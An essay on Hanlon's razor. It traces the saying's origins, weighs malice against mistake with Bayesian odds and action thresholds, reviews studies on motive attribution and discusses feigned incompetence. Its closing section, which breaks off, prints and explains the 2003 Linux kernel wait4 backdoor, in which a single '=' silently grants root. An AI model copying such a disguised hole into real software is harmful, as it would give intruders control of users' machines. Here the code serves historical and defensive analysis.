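# Hanlon's Razor: When to Read Apparent Malice as a Mistake and When as Deliberate Design

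## What the razor says and how to weigh malice against mistake

Hanlon's razor is a rule of thumb for explaining why people cause harm: "Never attribute to malice that which is adequately explained by stupidity." In philosophy, a razor is a rule for cutting away unlikely explanations. The best known, Occam's razor, favours the explanation with the fewest assumptions, and Hanlon's razor is named after it. People use Hanlon's razor when a colleague fails to reply, when a government office loses a file, or when software does damage and nobody can tell whether anyone intended it.

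"Stupidity" is too harsh a word for most cases. A driver who misses a road sign in fog, for example, is not stupid. The word *mistake* covers harm caused by gaps in knowledge or skill, lapses of attention, or circumstances. *Malice* covers harm caused by bad aims or motives, such as a wish to harm, deceive or gain unfairly. Reading a mistake as malice is a false accusation, and reading malice as a mistake is missed malice. People who follow the razor make fewer false accusations but miss some malice. Whether that tradeoff is worthwhile depends on how common malice is in the setting and how much harm each error does, and the razor contains no information about either.

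### Where the saying comes from

The sentence appeared in print in 1980, on page 52 of *Murphy's Law Book Two*, Arthur Bloch's second collection of joking laws about how things go wrong. Bloch printed it under Hanlon's name without explaining who Hanlon was. In December 1984, Glenn Harris called the rule "cryptically named" in the magazine *Infosystems*. His article is the earliest press use listed in Word Spy's *Hanlon's Razor*.

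Programmers kept the line in circulation. The Jargon File, a glossary of programmers' slang, describes it in the entry *Hanlon's Razor* as a particular favourite of hackers (in the old sense of keen programmers), who put it in their email signatures and on login screens. For years the glossary's editors did not know where the line came from. In the version of the entry that Limeback (2000) copied to a mailing list in *The New Hacker's Dictionary*, they guessed that "Hanlon" was a garbled "Heinlein", after the science fiction writer Robert A. Heinlein.

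In November 2001 Quentin Stafford-Fraser published on his blog, under the title *Hanlon's Razor*, an email from Joseph Bigler, who wrote that the razor's author was his late friend Robert J. Hanlon of Scranton, Pennsylvania. The people behind the first Murphy's law book had invited readers to send in laws for a sequel. They accepted Hanlon's, and his prize was ten copies of the new book, one of which he gave to Bigler. Bigler misquoted the razor in that email, but he supplied the exact wording, the page and the chapter title ("Advanced Expertsmanship") in a second one, which Stafford-Fraser published soon afterwards in *The origins of Hanlon's Razor*.

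Mardy Grothe, a compiler of quotations, later heard a similar story from Hanlon's widow and son, and added that Hanlon had worked as a computer programmer at the Tobyhanna Army Depot. The blog post *Hanlon's razor* (2024) quotes Grothe's account and the findings of Garson O'Toole, who traces sayings to their sources on the website Quote Investigator and also credits Hanlon. All the witnesses are friends or family, and Bigler wrote two decades after the event, but the printed book confirms the name, the date and the wording. The Jargon File's editors remain cautious and write only that "it is claimed".

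They also get the wording slightly wrong, writing "can be adequately explained" where Bloch has "is". This common variant loosens the rule a good deal, because with enough ingenuity one can think up a mistake that would account for almost anything. Bloch's wording sets a harder test, that a mistake does account for what happened.

The idea behind Hanlon's razor is much older than its wording. In Goethe's *The Sorrows of Young Werther* (1774), Werther looks into a family quarrel over a legacy, part of which his mother says his aunt is holding back. He rightly visits the aunt, hears her reasons and her terms for giving up the whole, and concludes that "misunderstandings and neglect cause more mischief in the world than malice or wickedness". He adds that malice and wickedness are, at any rate, much rarer. That second remark gives a starting estimate for any single case before the details are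 known, whereas the first concerns the total harm in the world and is of little help in judging one person.

The closest forerunner is Heinlein's story *Logic of Empire*, published in *Astounding Science-Fiction* in 1941. Its hero, Wingate, has escaped from forced labour on Venus and written a book against the colonial system. He shows it to Doc, a former professor of economics and philosophy, who tells him that he has fallen for the "devil theory": "You have attributed conditions to villainy that simply result from stupidity." But Doc then mostly blames economic conditions rather than stupidity. He argues that bankers and officials are not scoundrels but act under necessity and invent justifications afterwards, and that an antiquated financial structure produces slavery automatically. He falls back on "simple stupidity" only when Wingate insists on "human cussedness", and he admits that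 he cannot prove it. Nobody knows whether Hanlon had read the story. The Jargon File calls the evidence for Napoleon, another supposed author of the razor, dubious.

Hanlon's razor rests more on Werther's point that malice is rare than on simplicity. O'Toole groups it with Occam's razor as a tool for pruning hypotheses "by favoring simplicity", which is only partly right. A mistake is sometimes the more complicated explanation, as when three unrelated slips would all have had to happen on the same afternoon.

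### What the choice between malice and mistake leaves out

Many real cases contain both malice and mistake, so it helps to judge each act separately rather than look for one label for the whole incident. If an engineer miscalculates a load, notices a week later, and alters the records to hide the error, the calculation was a mistake and the cover-up was malice. A single act can also have mixed motives. A landlord who has never bothered to learn the fire code is ignorant of it, but he may have stayed that way because complying would cost him money.

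Another awkward case is what criminal lawyers call oblique intent, in which someone foresees that their action will cause harm, does not aim at the harm, and acts anyway. For example, a factory owner might dump waste because it is cheap, knowing that it will poison the river but not wanting to poison anyone. *Extending counterfactual accounts of intent to include oblique intent* (2021), a paper on judging the behaviour of algorithms, warns that a narrow definition of intent lets people label unacceptable outcomes as unintended side effects. It proposes a formal definition of oblique intent based on counterfactuals, meaning what would have happened had the actor chosen differently. One practical advantage of this definition is that people can use it without knowing the actor's utility function, the full ranking of what the actor wants. Under the definitions of malice and mistake given above,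 the factory owner acts with malice if the saving counts as an unfair gain, which it surely does, but other cases of foreseen harm are harder to classify.

Douglas Hubbard, a writer on risk management, thinks that malice and stupidity are often both the wrong explanation. In *The “Four Horsemen” of Risk Management*, a chapter of his book *The Failure of Risk Management* (second edition, 2020), he adds a corollary that he calls clumsier but more accurate. It says not to blame malice or stupidity for what can be explained by "moderately rational individuals following incentives in a complex system". People who pursue their own interests without coordination can, he argues, produce a result that looks like a conspiracy or an epidemic of ignorance. Suppose a bank pays its staff for each loan they approve and then sells the loans on. The staff approve weak loans, the buyers trust the bank's name,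 and the eventual collapse looks planned. Heinlein's Doc makes much the same argument about Venus. Because incentives are part of the circumstances, such cases usually count as mistakes in the broad sense, unless somebody set up the incentives to profit from the damage.

Grey's law is that "any sufficiently advanced incompetence is indistinguishable from malice." The blog post *Magic, stupidity, and malice* (2009) explains that the law combines Hanlon's razor with the science fiction writer Arthur C. Clarke's remark that sufficiently advanced technology is indistinguishable from magic. According to Plankers's *Grey's Law* (2007), nobody knows who Grey was. Though phrased as a joke, the law makes the serious claim that bad enough incompetence leaves the same traces as malice, so the damage alone can't show which one caused it. Telling them apart takes other evidence, such as how the same person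 behaves when nothing is at stake.

### The odds form of Bayes' rule

Bayes' rule is the formula in probability theory for revising a belief in the light of evidence. When there are two explanations to compare, the handiest version uses odds. Write *M* for malice, *S* for mistake and *E* for the evidence. The rule gives $P(M|E) = P(E|M)\,P(M)/P(E)$ for malice and $P(S|E) = P(E|S)\,P(S)/P(E)$ for mistake. Dividing the first by the second makes the awkward term $P(E)$ cancel:

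$$\frac{P(M|E)}{P(S|E)} = \frac{P(M)}{P(S)} \times \frac{P(E|M)}{P(E|S)}$$

The posterior odds equal the prior odds multiplied by the likelihood ratio. The prior odds are how probable malice is relative to mistake before considering the evidence of the case. The likelihood ratio is how probable the evidence is if there was malice, divided by how probable it is if there was a mistake.

Suppose, with invented numbers, that a colleague organises a meeting and leaves Anna off the invitation. In her office, one such omission is deliberate for every 1,000 that are slips, so the prior odds of malice are 1 to 1,000. Anna then learns that the meeting settled the budget for her project. Someone who wanted her out of the way would choose a meeting like that about half the time. A slip could affect any meeting, and only one meeting in a hundred concerns her budget. The likelihood ratio is therefore 0.5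 / 0.01 = 50, and the posterior odds are 50 to 1,000, or 1 to 20, which is a probability of 1/21, a little under 5%. Malice is now nearly fifty times as probable as it was, but a slip is still much more likely.

Now suppose it happens again at the next budget meeting. Multiplying by another 50 would bring the odds to 2.5 to 1 in favour of malice, but this is valid only if the two omissions would be independent if both were mistakes. If the organiser is working from an old address list, a single error produces both. The second omission was then almost certain to follow the first, so its likelihood ratio is close to 1, as it would be for any further omissions. Anna would learn more by checking whether she is also missing from the dull meetings, since an old list would leave her out of those too and a schemer would have no reason to.

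How she found the evidence also matters. If she searched a hundred past omissions for a suspicious one, the chance that at least one fell on a budget meeting by accident is about 63%, so finding one should not surprise her, even though the same coincidence would be striking in a single case.

The prior odds affect the result most in this example, and they vary widely between settings. The Jargon File suggests that hackers may like the razor because they spend their days in environments built by "well-intentioned but short-sighted people". Prior odds of 1 to 1,000 may be about right there. If Anna's colleague has a record of shutting rivals out, the prior odds might be 1 to 10, and the same budget meeting raises them to 5 to 1, an 83% probability of malice. So two people can agree on the facts of a case and how much weight each fact deserves, yet reach opposite verdicts because they disagree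 about how common malice is in that setting.

(Turning odds into a probability in this way assumes that malice and mistake are the only candidates. If some third explanation is in play, the odds between the two are still correct but both probabilities shrink.)

### What "adequately explained" does and does not settle

Saying that a mistake adequately explains a harm means that evidence like this would be unsurprising if someone had made a mistake, which is a claim about $P(E|S)$ alone. Deciding between malice and mistake also requires $P(E|M)$, the probability of the same evidence given malice, and the prior odds of malice versus mistake.

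Doctors make a similar mistake with test results. *An Intuitive Explanation of Bayes's Theorem* describes studies in which most doctors knew that about 80% of women with breast cancer have a positive mammogram, and concluded that a woman with a positive mammogram has about an 80% chance of cancer. The doctors used only one of the three numbers they needed, leaving out how common cancer is among the women screened and how often healthy women test positive. Suppose those numbers are 1% and 10%. Among 1,000 women, there would be 8 true positives and 99 false ones, so a woman who tests positive would have about a 7% chance of cancer. Someone who applies the razor literally also uses only one number, though a different one. *Hanlon's Razor* (Ballantyne and Ditto, 2021) offers a more careful reading.

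Because no probability can exceed 1, the likelihood ratio can never be larger than $1/P(E|S)$. If a mistake would produce the evidence half the time, the evidence can at most double the odds of malice. Someone who started at odds of 1 to 1,000 would end no higher than 1 to 500, however well malice fits the facts. The razor therefore gives the right verdict when malice is rare and a mistake would easily have produced what people saw. If either condition doesn't hold, the razor can fail, as these invented cases show.

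| Case | Prior odds of malice | P(E) if malice | P(E) if mistake | Likelihood ratio | Probability of malice |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Malice rare, mistake fits well | 1 to 1,000 | 0.9 | 0.5 | 1.8 | 0.2% |
| Malice common, mistake fits well | 1 to 1 | 0.9 | 0.5 | 1.8 | 64% |
| Malice rare, neither fits well | 1 to 1,000 | 0.002 | 0.001 | 2 | 0.2% |
| Malice rare, only malice fits well | 1 to 1,000 | 0.5 | 0.0001 | 5,000 | 83% |

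In the second row, malice is the better bet even though a mistake explains the evidence as adequately as it does in the first. In the third row, malice explains the evidence hardly any better than a mistake does, but people tend to infer malice because a mistake explains it badly. Any sufficiently detailed record, such as one with exact words and a time of 14:07, is improbable under every explanation, so what matters is how much more probable it is under one explanation than under the other.

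A bigger problem is that people who know how others reason can feign incompetence to make malice look like a mistake. The better they do this, the closer the likelihood ratio gets to 1, where the evidence leaves the odds unchanged. A commenter on the Effective Altruism Forum, in *Never attribute to malice that which is adequately explained by stupidity*, makes this point about FTX, the cryptocurrency exchange that collapsed in 2022. Another participant had argued that its founder, Sam Bankman-Fried, showed bad judgement rather than malice, partly because he said so himself. The commenter replied that a denial is very weak evidence, because one would expect it from guilty and innocent people alike. If 99% of innocent people and 95% of guilty ones would deny the charge, the likelihood ratio is 0.96, so a denial barely changes the odds.

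The same commenter argues that malicious acts can often be explained by incompetence because the people who commit them design them that way, and that a community known for applying the razor invites people to take advantage of it. The first claim is sound when the harm took planning and the planner had something to lose if discovered. It is much weaker for a rude remark or a missed deadline, which hardly anyone bothers to disguise. The second claim implies that the prior odds of malice can change, because a group that forgives every apparent mistake can expect to attract people who disguise harm as mistakes. The commenter would keep the razor as a heuristic but let moderate evidence overturn it.

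### Taking precautions while believing in a mistake

So far the question has been what to believe. What to do is a separate question, and answering the first settles the second less often than the razor's wording suggests.

Let *p* be the probability of malice. A precaution has a cost *C* if it turns out to have been needless, and it prevents a loss *L* if there is malice. (*L* is the net figure, after subtracting what the precaution costs in that case.) On average the precaution saves $pL$ and wastes $(1-p)C$. It is worth taking when $pL > (1-p)C$, and solving for *p* gives the action threshold, the probability of malice above which the precaution is worth its cost:

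$$p^* = \frac{C}{C+L}$$

Anna puts the probability of malice at about 5%. She could write to the head of department, mention that she seems to have dropped off the list, and ask for a chance to comment before the budget is final. If nobody meant any harm, the message takes her a few minutes and is slightly awkward, which we can value at, say, $20. If somebody did, it saves her project $5,000. The threshold is 20 / 5,020, or about 0.4%, and her estimate of 5% is well above it. She should write the message even though she is 95% sure that it was a slip.

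She could instead accuse her colleague in front of the team. A false accusation would ruin a working relationship she values at $20,000, while a true one would save the same $5,000. The accusation is therefore worth making only if the probability of malice is above 20,000 / 25,000, or 80%, and her estimate is far below that. The same estimate justifies sending the message but not making the accusation. Many arguments about whether to "assume malice" confuse these two actions. The dollar figures are guesses, but the two thresholds differ by a factor of 200, so the conclusion holds even if the guesses are fairly bad.

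Many precautions also catch honest mistakes, which lowers *C* further. If Anna's message gets an old address list corrected, it was worth sending even if there was no malice. This is the practical side of Grey's law. When the same measure protects against both incompetence and malice, one can often take it without deciding which is present.

Software illustrates this well because strangers can propose changes to programs that millions of people run. Anyone may read, copy and modify the code of open-source software. A commit is a set of changes to that code, saved with a name, a date and a short description. A contributor proposes commits to a project by opening a pull request, which others can inspect and discuss first. Maintainers decide which changes enter the project. A backdoor is a hidden way into a system that someone added on purpose. A sock puppet is a false account that its owner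 uses to pose as an independent person.

Suppose that a careful review of a pull request takes $100 worth of a maintainer's time, and that a backdoor would do $10 million of damage. The action threshold for the review is then about 1 in 100,000. If one stranger in 10,000 is hiding a backdoor, reviewing every stranger's code is worth ten times what it costs, even though the maintainer is right to think each of them almost certainly honest. Now suppose that an honest contributor is worth $5,000 in future work, and that reviewers miss one backdoor in ten, so that banning strangers would prevent a further $1 million of expected damage from each attacker. The threshold for the ban is about 1 in 200, so at one attacker in 10,000 the maintainer should keep accepting strangers' contributions.

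If four independent people vouch for a newcomer, and each recommendation is five times as likely for an honest contributor as for an attacker, together they divide the odds of malice by 625. If the newcomer runs all four accounts as sock puppets, the recommendations are no evidence of honesty, and a maintainer who suspects this has to raise the odds again. Attackers used sock puppets in the campaign to take over xz Utils, a widely used compression tool.

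## Is the razor good advice?

The philosopher Nathan Ballantyne and the psychologist Peter Ditto knew of no earlier philosophical or scientific work devoted to the principle when they wrote *Hanlon's Razor* (2021). They consider two reasons for following it. The razor might make people's judgements more accurate, or it might make people more charitable towards their opponents, even if it made their judgements somewhat less accurate. They find serious gaps in both arguments.

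They begin by sorting the causes of error into moral defects and epistemic ones, which have to do with knowledge and reasoning. Moral defects include spite, cruelty, pride, prejudice, lack of empathy and unwarranted self-interest. Epistemic defects include bad reasoning, missing information, lapses of attention, and circumstances that would mislead even someone who reasoned flawlessly. The two groups correspond roughly to malice and mistake, but the moral list includes more than most people would call malice. If a manager counts as malicious because he never thinks about how the night shift gets home, malice is much more common than if only ill will counts, and a presumption against it is harder to defend.

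Their sharpened razor applies when malice and stupidity are both plausible explanations of someone's error. In that case, one should not blame a moral defect if an epistemic defect explains the error adequately, though evidence can still overturn this presumption. The rule therefore doesn't cover clear cases. Nobody suspects malice when a person gets an easy sum wrong, or blames missing information when a person sees nothing wrong with torturing the innocent for fun. The rule does cover a neighbour with objectionable views on immigration, who may lack compassion or may have believed a misleading pundit.

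The weak point in this version is the word "plausible", because the observer decides what is plausible. Someone who already despises the neighbour will find ignorance an implausible excuse and so will never apply the rule.

### Do people see too much malice?

The argument from accuracy has two premises: people's negative moral judgements are systematically biased in some kinds of conflict, and following the razor can make those biased judgements more accurate. Ballantyne and Ditto grant the first premise based on several psychology experiments and direct most of their criticism at the second. But the experiments deserve a closer look because they measure quite different things.

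The social psychologist Glenn Reeder and his colleagues asked pro-war and antiwar Americans about each other's motives. According to a press account quoted in the blog post *None Evil or All Evil?*, both groups thought people who agreed with them acted on principle and people who disagreed acted out of narrow self-interest. Ballantyne and Ditto, citing the team's 2005 paper, add that this tendency was strongest among those most involved in the issue. Participants also doubted that their opponents knew their own motives.

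Mutual suspicion of this sort shows that somebody is wrong, but not who. Both camps may be principled and judging each other unfairly, or both may be selfish, in which case each is right about its opponents but wrong about itself.

Waytz, Young and Ginges (2014), in *Motive attribution asymmetry for love vs. hate drives intractable conflict*, studied the same pattern between groups. They asked 285 American Democrats and Republicans how much one of the two parties was motivated by love of its own side and how much by hatred of the other. People rated their own party higher on love (4.47) than hate (3.63), and the opposing party higher on hate (4.56) than love (3.53). The researchers then asked representative samples of 497 Israelis and 1,266 Palestinians why many people on each side supported violence. The average ratings were as follows.

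| Who judged | Whose motives | Love of own side | Hatred of other side |
|---|---|---|---|
| Israelis | Israelis | 3.10 | 2.30 |
| Israelis | Palestinians | 2.23 | 3.27 |
| Palestinians | Palestinians | 3.34 | 3.29 |
| Palestinians | Israelis | 2.77 | 3.45 |

Waytz and colleagues use "bias" to mean a tendency to answer in a certain way, and they say explicitly that they do not mean error. We can still check roughly for error by comparing each group's ratings of itself in the table with the other group's ratings of it, although self-reports are hardly a neutral standard. Palestinians rated Israeli hatred far higher than Israelis did, but Israelis' rating of Palestinian hatred (3.27) was almost the same as the Palestinians' own (3.29). Israelis did rate Palestinian love lower than Palestinians did.

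The razor would not have helped much in either case. Love of one's own people is a motive, not a mistake, so someone who replaced "they hate us" with "they are confused" would be no nearer the truth. Money worked better in a further study of 331 Democrats and Republicans, in which Waytz and colleagues offered some participants a payment for judging the other party accurately. Participants without the offer rated the other party at 5.27 for hate and 3.89 for love, while those with it reversed the order, with ratings of 4.35 and 4.70. The money may have made people think harder, or they may have guessed which answer would earn it, but either way their first answers weren't fixed convictions.

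The experiment closest to the razor is in *The worst-motive fallacy* (Walmsley and O'Madagain, 2020). It gave each of 323 people one of four stories about a character who has a good motive and a bad motive for the same plan. In one story, a politician wants to hire an engineer, partly because he needs work and partly so that he will trick her opponent's supporters into voting on the wrong day. He refuses to trick anyone. She can now give him ordinary maintenance work, which satisfies only the kind motive, or hire a hacker, which satisfies only the dishonest one. Participants predicted her choice, said what they would do themselves, and rated each motive from −10 (very bad) to +10 (very good).

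Participants were more likely to expect a character to act on the bad motive the worse they rated it relative to the good one (p = 0.016). The analysis adjusted for how extreme each motive was, measured by how far its rating lay from zero, because people expect others to act on a strong motive over a weak one, whether it is good or bad. Participants also expected the characters to behave worse than they themselves would.

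Walmsley and O'Madagain then repeated the experiment with 967 people and twelve stories, after registering their plan. The gap between self and others appeared again, but the main effect did not appear overall. It appeared in the four original stories but not in the eight new ones. The researchers also excluded 41% of the responses, mostly because people failed attention checks or took the test more than once. They warn that this raises doubts about data quality.

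They say the bias was hidden because the good motives in the new stories were more extreme than the bad ones (on average 7.4 points from zero against 5.6). They may be right, but they came up with this explanation after seeing the results. It also fits poorly with their method, which adjusted for extremeness to keep it from hiding or mimicking the effect. Ballantyne and Ditto cite the fallacy without mentioning the failed replication. A later conference poster, *The Worst-Motive Fallacy* (2023), reports that 53 adolescent girls rated themselves morally above the characters in every scenario, but this supports only the gap between self and others.

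Expecting the worst of these characters is also not clearly a fallacy. Planning to cheat voters is rarer than wanting to help an unemployed acquaintance, so we learn more about the politician from the plan to cheat. A reader who predicts that she will hire the hacker may be reasoning well, and since the politician is fictional, no fact could prove the reader wrong.

The side-effect effect is a much sturdier finding. *Intentional action and side effects in ordinary language* (Knobe, 2003) demonstrated it with 78 people in a Manhattan park. In the story they read, a company's vice-president tells the chairman that a new programme will increase profits but also harm the environment. The chairman answers that he doesn't care about the environment and wants the profit. The programme goes ahead and harms the environment. Of those who read this version, 82% said the chairman harmed the environment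 intentionally. When Knobe changed "harm" to "help" and almost nothing else, only 23% said he helped it intentionally. In a second experiment, 42 people read about a lieutenant who cares about capturing a hill but not about his soldiers, and the figures were 77% for harm and 30% for help.

*Many Labs 2* (Klein and colleagues, 2018) repeated the chairman experiment with 7,982 people and found a somewhat larger effect than the original (1.75 standard deviations, compared with 1.45). Only about half of the 28 findings it retested held up. FORRT's *Intentional action and side effects in ordinary language*, an entry in an atlas of replications, lists a second successful replication of the experiment.

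Some philosophers suspect that people say "intentionally" here only because denying it would sound like making excuses for the chairman. Sytsma, Bishop and Schwenkler tested this in *Has the Side-Effect Effect been cancelled?* by asking 67 people to rank four statements, two of which blamed him. Participants could blame him without calling the harm intentional, but 52% ranked first the statement that he harmed the environment intentionally and was to blame, and 21% the statement that he was to blame but had not done it intentionally.

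So people seem to mean what they say about the chairman, but his case has little bearing on the razor, because he made no mistake. He knew about the harm and accepted it for money, which criminal lawyers call oblique intent. Knobe's effect shows that people count foreseen harm as intentional, but it doesn't show that they mistake accidents for deliberate schemes.

People can give too little weight to the circumstances behind someone's behaviour, even when they know about them. The best evidence of this error, which is relevant to the razor, comes from an experiment that didn't involve malice. Klein and colleagues asked 7,197 people to read a student's essay for or against the death penalty, then told them that the student had been assigned that side. When participants rated the student's real opinion on a 15-point scale, they still gave writers of essays for the death penalty an average of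 11.0 and writers of essays against it 4.5. People who make the same error about a missed deadline or a lost file will blame character too often.

### Why a bias does not show that malice is rare

Even if people see too much malice, mistakes aren't necessarily more common than malice in any particular setting. Suppose 10 out of 100 ambiguous incidents in an office are malicious. A suspicious observer who calls 30 of them malicious, including those 10, is wrong 20 times. A colleague who follows the razor and calls every incident a mistake is wrong only 10 times.

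If the same two people work in a marketplace full of swindlers, 70 of the 100 incidents might be malicious. The suspicious observer calls 90 malicious, including all 70, and is again wrong 20 times. Her colleague, who follows the razor, is wrong 70 times. She overestimates malice by the same amount in both places, but the razor halves the errors in the first and more than triples them in the marketplace. Experiments on bias can at best measure how far judgement departs from the truth. Learning how common malice is requires investigating actual cases and counting the malicious ones.

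Ballantyne and Ditto reach a similar conclusion. The razor would improve accuracy across conflicts in general only if stupidity were more common in them than malice, and they see no good reason to assume that. Some people err mainly from badness, and their example is Pol Pot. Others err from both badness and stupidity. Richard Nixon's men broke into the office of the psychiatrist treating Daniel Ellsberg, who had leaked the Pentagon Papers, and the order to do so was arguably both wicked and stupid. And in many disputes one side is simply right, so it has no error to explain. This last point is less damaging than the others, because the razor is advice about errors, and someone who is wrong about who erred needs different advice.

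They also doubt that reading the razor changes how anyone thinks, because merely warning people about a bias usually doesn't remove it. Researchers could test this by showing the razor to half of their participants, asking everyone to judge ambiguous incidents whose true causes are known, and counting false accusations and missed malice separately. Nobody appears to have published such an experiment.

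### The argument from charity

Perhaps we should judge the razor by its effects rather than its accuracy. The second argument for the razor is that following it can help people get along. According to this argument, people who see a conflict as a clash of goals and motives tend to be less cooperative, civil and tolerant than people who don't, and the razor can keep people from seeing a conflict that way.

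Some evidence supports the first premise. In a sample of 498 Israelis, Waytz and colleagues found that those who attributed Palestinian violence to hatred more than love were less willing to negotiate (a correlation of −0.23) and less willing to vote for a peace deal (−0.15). The correlations are modest, and the causation could run the other way, since someone who already opposes negotiating has a reason to think badly of the other side.

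The second premise is shakier. Ballantyne and Ditto speculate that the razor might work through vanity. Someone who moves from "my opponents are evil" to "my opponents are dumb" can feel clever and magnanimous, and may treat them better as a result. But the same feeling could make the person insufferable. Some people, such as a scientist who prizes intelligence above character, would also rather be thought wicked than stupid, and applying the razor to them could inflame the quarrel.

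Another difficulty is that people have trouble separating the razor's two explanations, because judgements of stupidity and badness influence each other. During the Covid-19 pandemic, many people who refused to wear masks were misinformed about whether masks worked. An observer could accept that explanation and still think the error so serious and so easy to correct that only a bad person would persist in it. Conversely, *Unethical and Inept?* (Stellar and Willer, 2019) found in six studies with 1,567 participants that people use information about someone's morals to judge that person's competence, even though they believe the two are independent.

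Keeping both explanations in mind also has a drawback, since it can make people less trusting. Ballantyne and Ditto cite experiments by Steven Fein and James Hilton, who defined suspicion as actively considering rival explanations of someone's motives. Suspicious people liked the other person less and were less willing to take that person's words at face value. Someone who uses the razor to move from certainty about malice to doubt may therefore become wary rather than charitable.

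The razor can also mislead people who don't know how an opponent came to believe something. They may search honestly for an innocent explanation, fail to find one, and conclude that he must be dishonest. Ballantyne and Ditto call this a method blind spot and suggest talking to the opponent to find out. Using the razor also means assuming that the other person is the one in error. To counter this, they propose a companion rule that people should seriously examine their own moral and intellectual competence before attributing either kind of defect to anyone else. This is sensible advice, but someone who followed it strictly would seldom use the razor.

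### Feigned incompetence

Both arguments face the problem that people can feign incompetence. Ballantyne and Ditto point out that people who mean harm may gladly give up some of their reputation for competence to protect their reputation for honesty. Saying "I just didn't know" does them little harm compared with dismissal or prison.

The Office of Strategic Services (OSS), the American wartime intelligence agency, turned this into a method. In January 1944 it issued the *Simple Sabotage Field Manual*, a guide for ordinary people in enemy-held countries who had no special training or equipment. Besides physical sabotage, the manual recommends ways to slow down an organisation from inside, such as insisting on official channels, referring questions to large committees, misunderstanding orders and misfiling papers. These were safe to do on purpose because every office has people who do them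 innocently. The manual tells saboteurs to favour acts that many people could have committed, and to apologise profusely and plead stupidity or ignorance if blamed.

The odds form of Bayes' rule shows why this works. Suppose, with invented numbers, that an honest clerk in a railway office misfiles 2% of the army's shipping orders, each independently of the others. A reckless saboteur misfiles 20%. If 20 orders out of 100 go astray, the likelihood ratio between the two explanations is about 9 trillion, and the clerk is finished whatever anyone thought of him before. A careful saboteur misfiles only 4%. If 4 orders out of 100 go astray, the likelihood ratio is

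$$\left(\frac{0.04}{0.02}\right)^{4} \times \left(\frac{0.96}{0.98}\right)^{96} \approx 2.2$$

In a peacetime office with one saboteur for every 1,000 honest clerks, the probability of sabotage after four lost orders is about 0.2%. In an occupied city where half of the clerks work for the resistance, it is 69% after the same four lost orders. If saboteurs disguised themselves perfectly, the likelihood ratio would fall to 1, and the probability of sabotage would depend entirely on how common saboteurs are.

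Disguise limits the damage a saboteur can do, however. If he misfiles 2% of the orders, as an honest clerk would, he does no more damage than the clerk unless he picks the orders that matter most, and then an investigator can look at which orders went missing instead of how many. The OSS could accept this limit because it hoped that many people would each do a little harm. Disguise is much less limiting when one act is enough, as with a backdoor, because the attacker doesn't have to repeat a convincing slip and create a pattern.

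An employer can also remove the reward for feigned incompetence by reassigning any clerk who loses four orders, whether he lost them deliberately or through carelessness.

### Advice for the suspicious and the trusting

The razor's defenders can reply that it was only meant to correct a tendency to assume the worst. In an article for the Irish broadcaster RTÉ, Walmsley and O'Madagain argue that people systematically err in this direction, so assuming the best of others is sometimes necessary as well as charitable. They suggest that a neighbour who plays loud music may seem not to care about you when in fact he thinks you like it too. The Decision Lab's *Hanlon's Razor* goes further, claiming that the razor is right on average because malice is probably much rarer than instinct suggests. But even if malice is rarer than people think, it could still be common.

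The defence is most persuasive when applied to people whose situation makes them too suspicious. Kramer (1994), in *The Sinister Attribution Error*, draws on research showing that people who feel self-conscious or under evaluation overestimate how much attention others pay them. They take others' behaviour too personally and become distrustful. An employee on probation whose manager walks past without a greeting might well benefit from the razor.

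Critics answer that the same advice also reaches people who already trust too much. Suppose the true probability of malice in some situation is 10%, a suspicious person puts it at 30%, a trusting person puts it at 4%, and the razor leads each to halve their estimate. The suspicious person's estimate falls to 15%, much closer to the truth, but the trusting person's falls to 2%, further from it. If a precaution is worth taking whenever the probability of malice is above 3%, the trusting person now drops it even though the true probability is well above that threshold, while the suspicious person takes it either way.

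Trusting people may also be more likely than suspicious people to use the razor. Ballantyne and Ditto observe that following it probably requires some intellectual humility, so many of the people who would benefit most won't use it. If humble people are also more willing to give others the benefit of the doubt, the people who follow the advice will mostly be those who need it least. Nobody has measured who uses the razor, so this is a guess, but it weakens the claim that the razor corrects a general bias.

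Critics can also draw on Walmsley and O'Madagain's own suggestion that suspicion may have evolved because trusting a malicious partner harmed our ancestors more than missing a chance to cooperate. Where overlooking malice is still the more harmful mistake, people have good reason to keep taking precautions even if they correct their beliefs.

Two of Ballantyne and Ditto's examples show how far apart the possible policies are. A darkly comic 1973 essay on how to swim with sharks recommends treating every unidentified fish as a shark. The other example is a story Joe Biden told at Yale in 2015. As a young senator, he had complained that his colleague Jesse Helms, who was fighting a bill to help disabled people, did not care about them. Mike Mansfield, the Senate majority leader, told Biden that Helms and his wife had adopted a disabled boy. He advised Biden to question other people's judgement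 but never their motives.

Neither policy makes anyone better at telling malice from mistake. The swimmer's policy reduces missed malice but leads to more false accusations, and Biden's does the reverse. Reducing both errors requires evidence about the particular person, which Mansfield had about Helms. Biden changed his mind because of the adoption, which he could not have inferred from a rule about motives.

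## Two deceptions aimed at the Linux kernel

The Linux kernel is the core of the Linux operating system and controls the hardware and what each program may do. Thousands of people contribute to it, most of whom have never met, and one wrong character can let an intruder take over a computer. Nearly all such errors are accidental, but in 2003 somebody planted one on purpose, and in 2020 two researchers submitted flawed code under false names to see whether maintainers would notice. When more bad code arrived from the researchers' university in 2021, a leading maintainer concluded, almost certainly wrongly, that it was another trick.

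### A missing equals sign in 2003

In 2003 the kernel's developers kept the master copy of its source code in BitKeeper, a commercial system for tracking changes. Some programmers refused to use BitKeeper, so its maker, BitMover, also published a copy through a free system called CVS. Developers submitted changes only to the master copy, and a program at BitMover then copied each one to the CVS version, with a pointer to the matching change in BitKeeper.

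On 5 November Larry McVoy of BitMover told the kernel mailing list that somebody had edited the CVS copy directly. In *BK2CVS problem*, McVoy (2003) listed three entries in the history of one file that had no pointer. All three carried the login name of David Miller, a trusted kernel developer, and were dated within 22 minutes of each other on the previous day. The first added two lines and had no description. The second removed 58 lines, and the third added 58 lines with a comment beginning "Oops" about having worked on the wrong file. Miller denied making any of them. McVoy thought someone might have tried to break into the server, but he called the matter no big deal and invited whoever was responsible to own up.

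Another developer asked out of curiosity what the two lines were. McVoy posted them:

```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

In C, the language of the kernel, `uid == 0` checks whether the current user's number is zero, while `uid = 0`, with one equals sign, sets it to zero. User number zero is root, the administrator, who can read every file and change every program on the machine.

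On a quick reading, the code looks like a routine check in `wait4`, a function that programs call to wait for another process. It seems to return an error if a program running as root calls `wait4` with a certain odd combination of options. In fact, if the options match that combination, the second half of the condition sets the program's user number to zero, which is root's number. C treats zero as false, so the condition fails and the error line never runs. Anyone who could already run a program on the machine could therefore become root by calling `wait4` with the right options.

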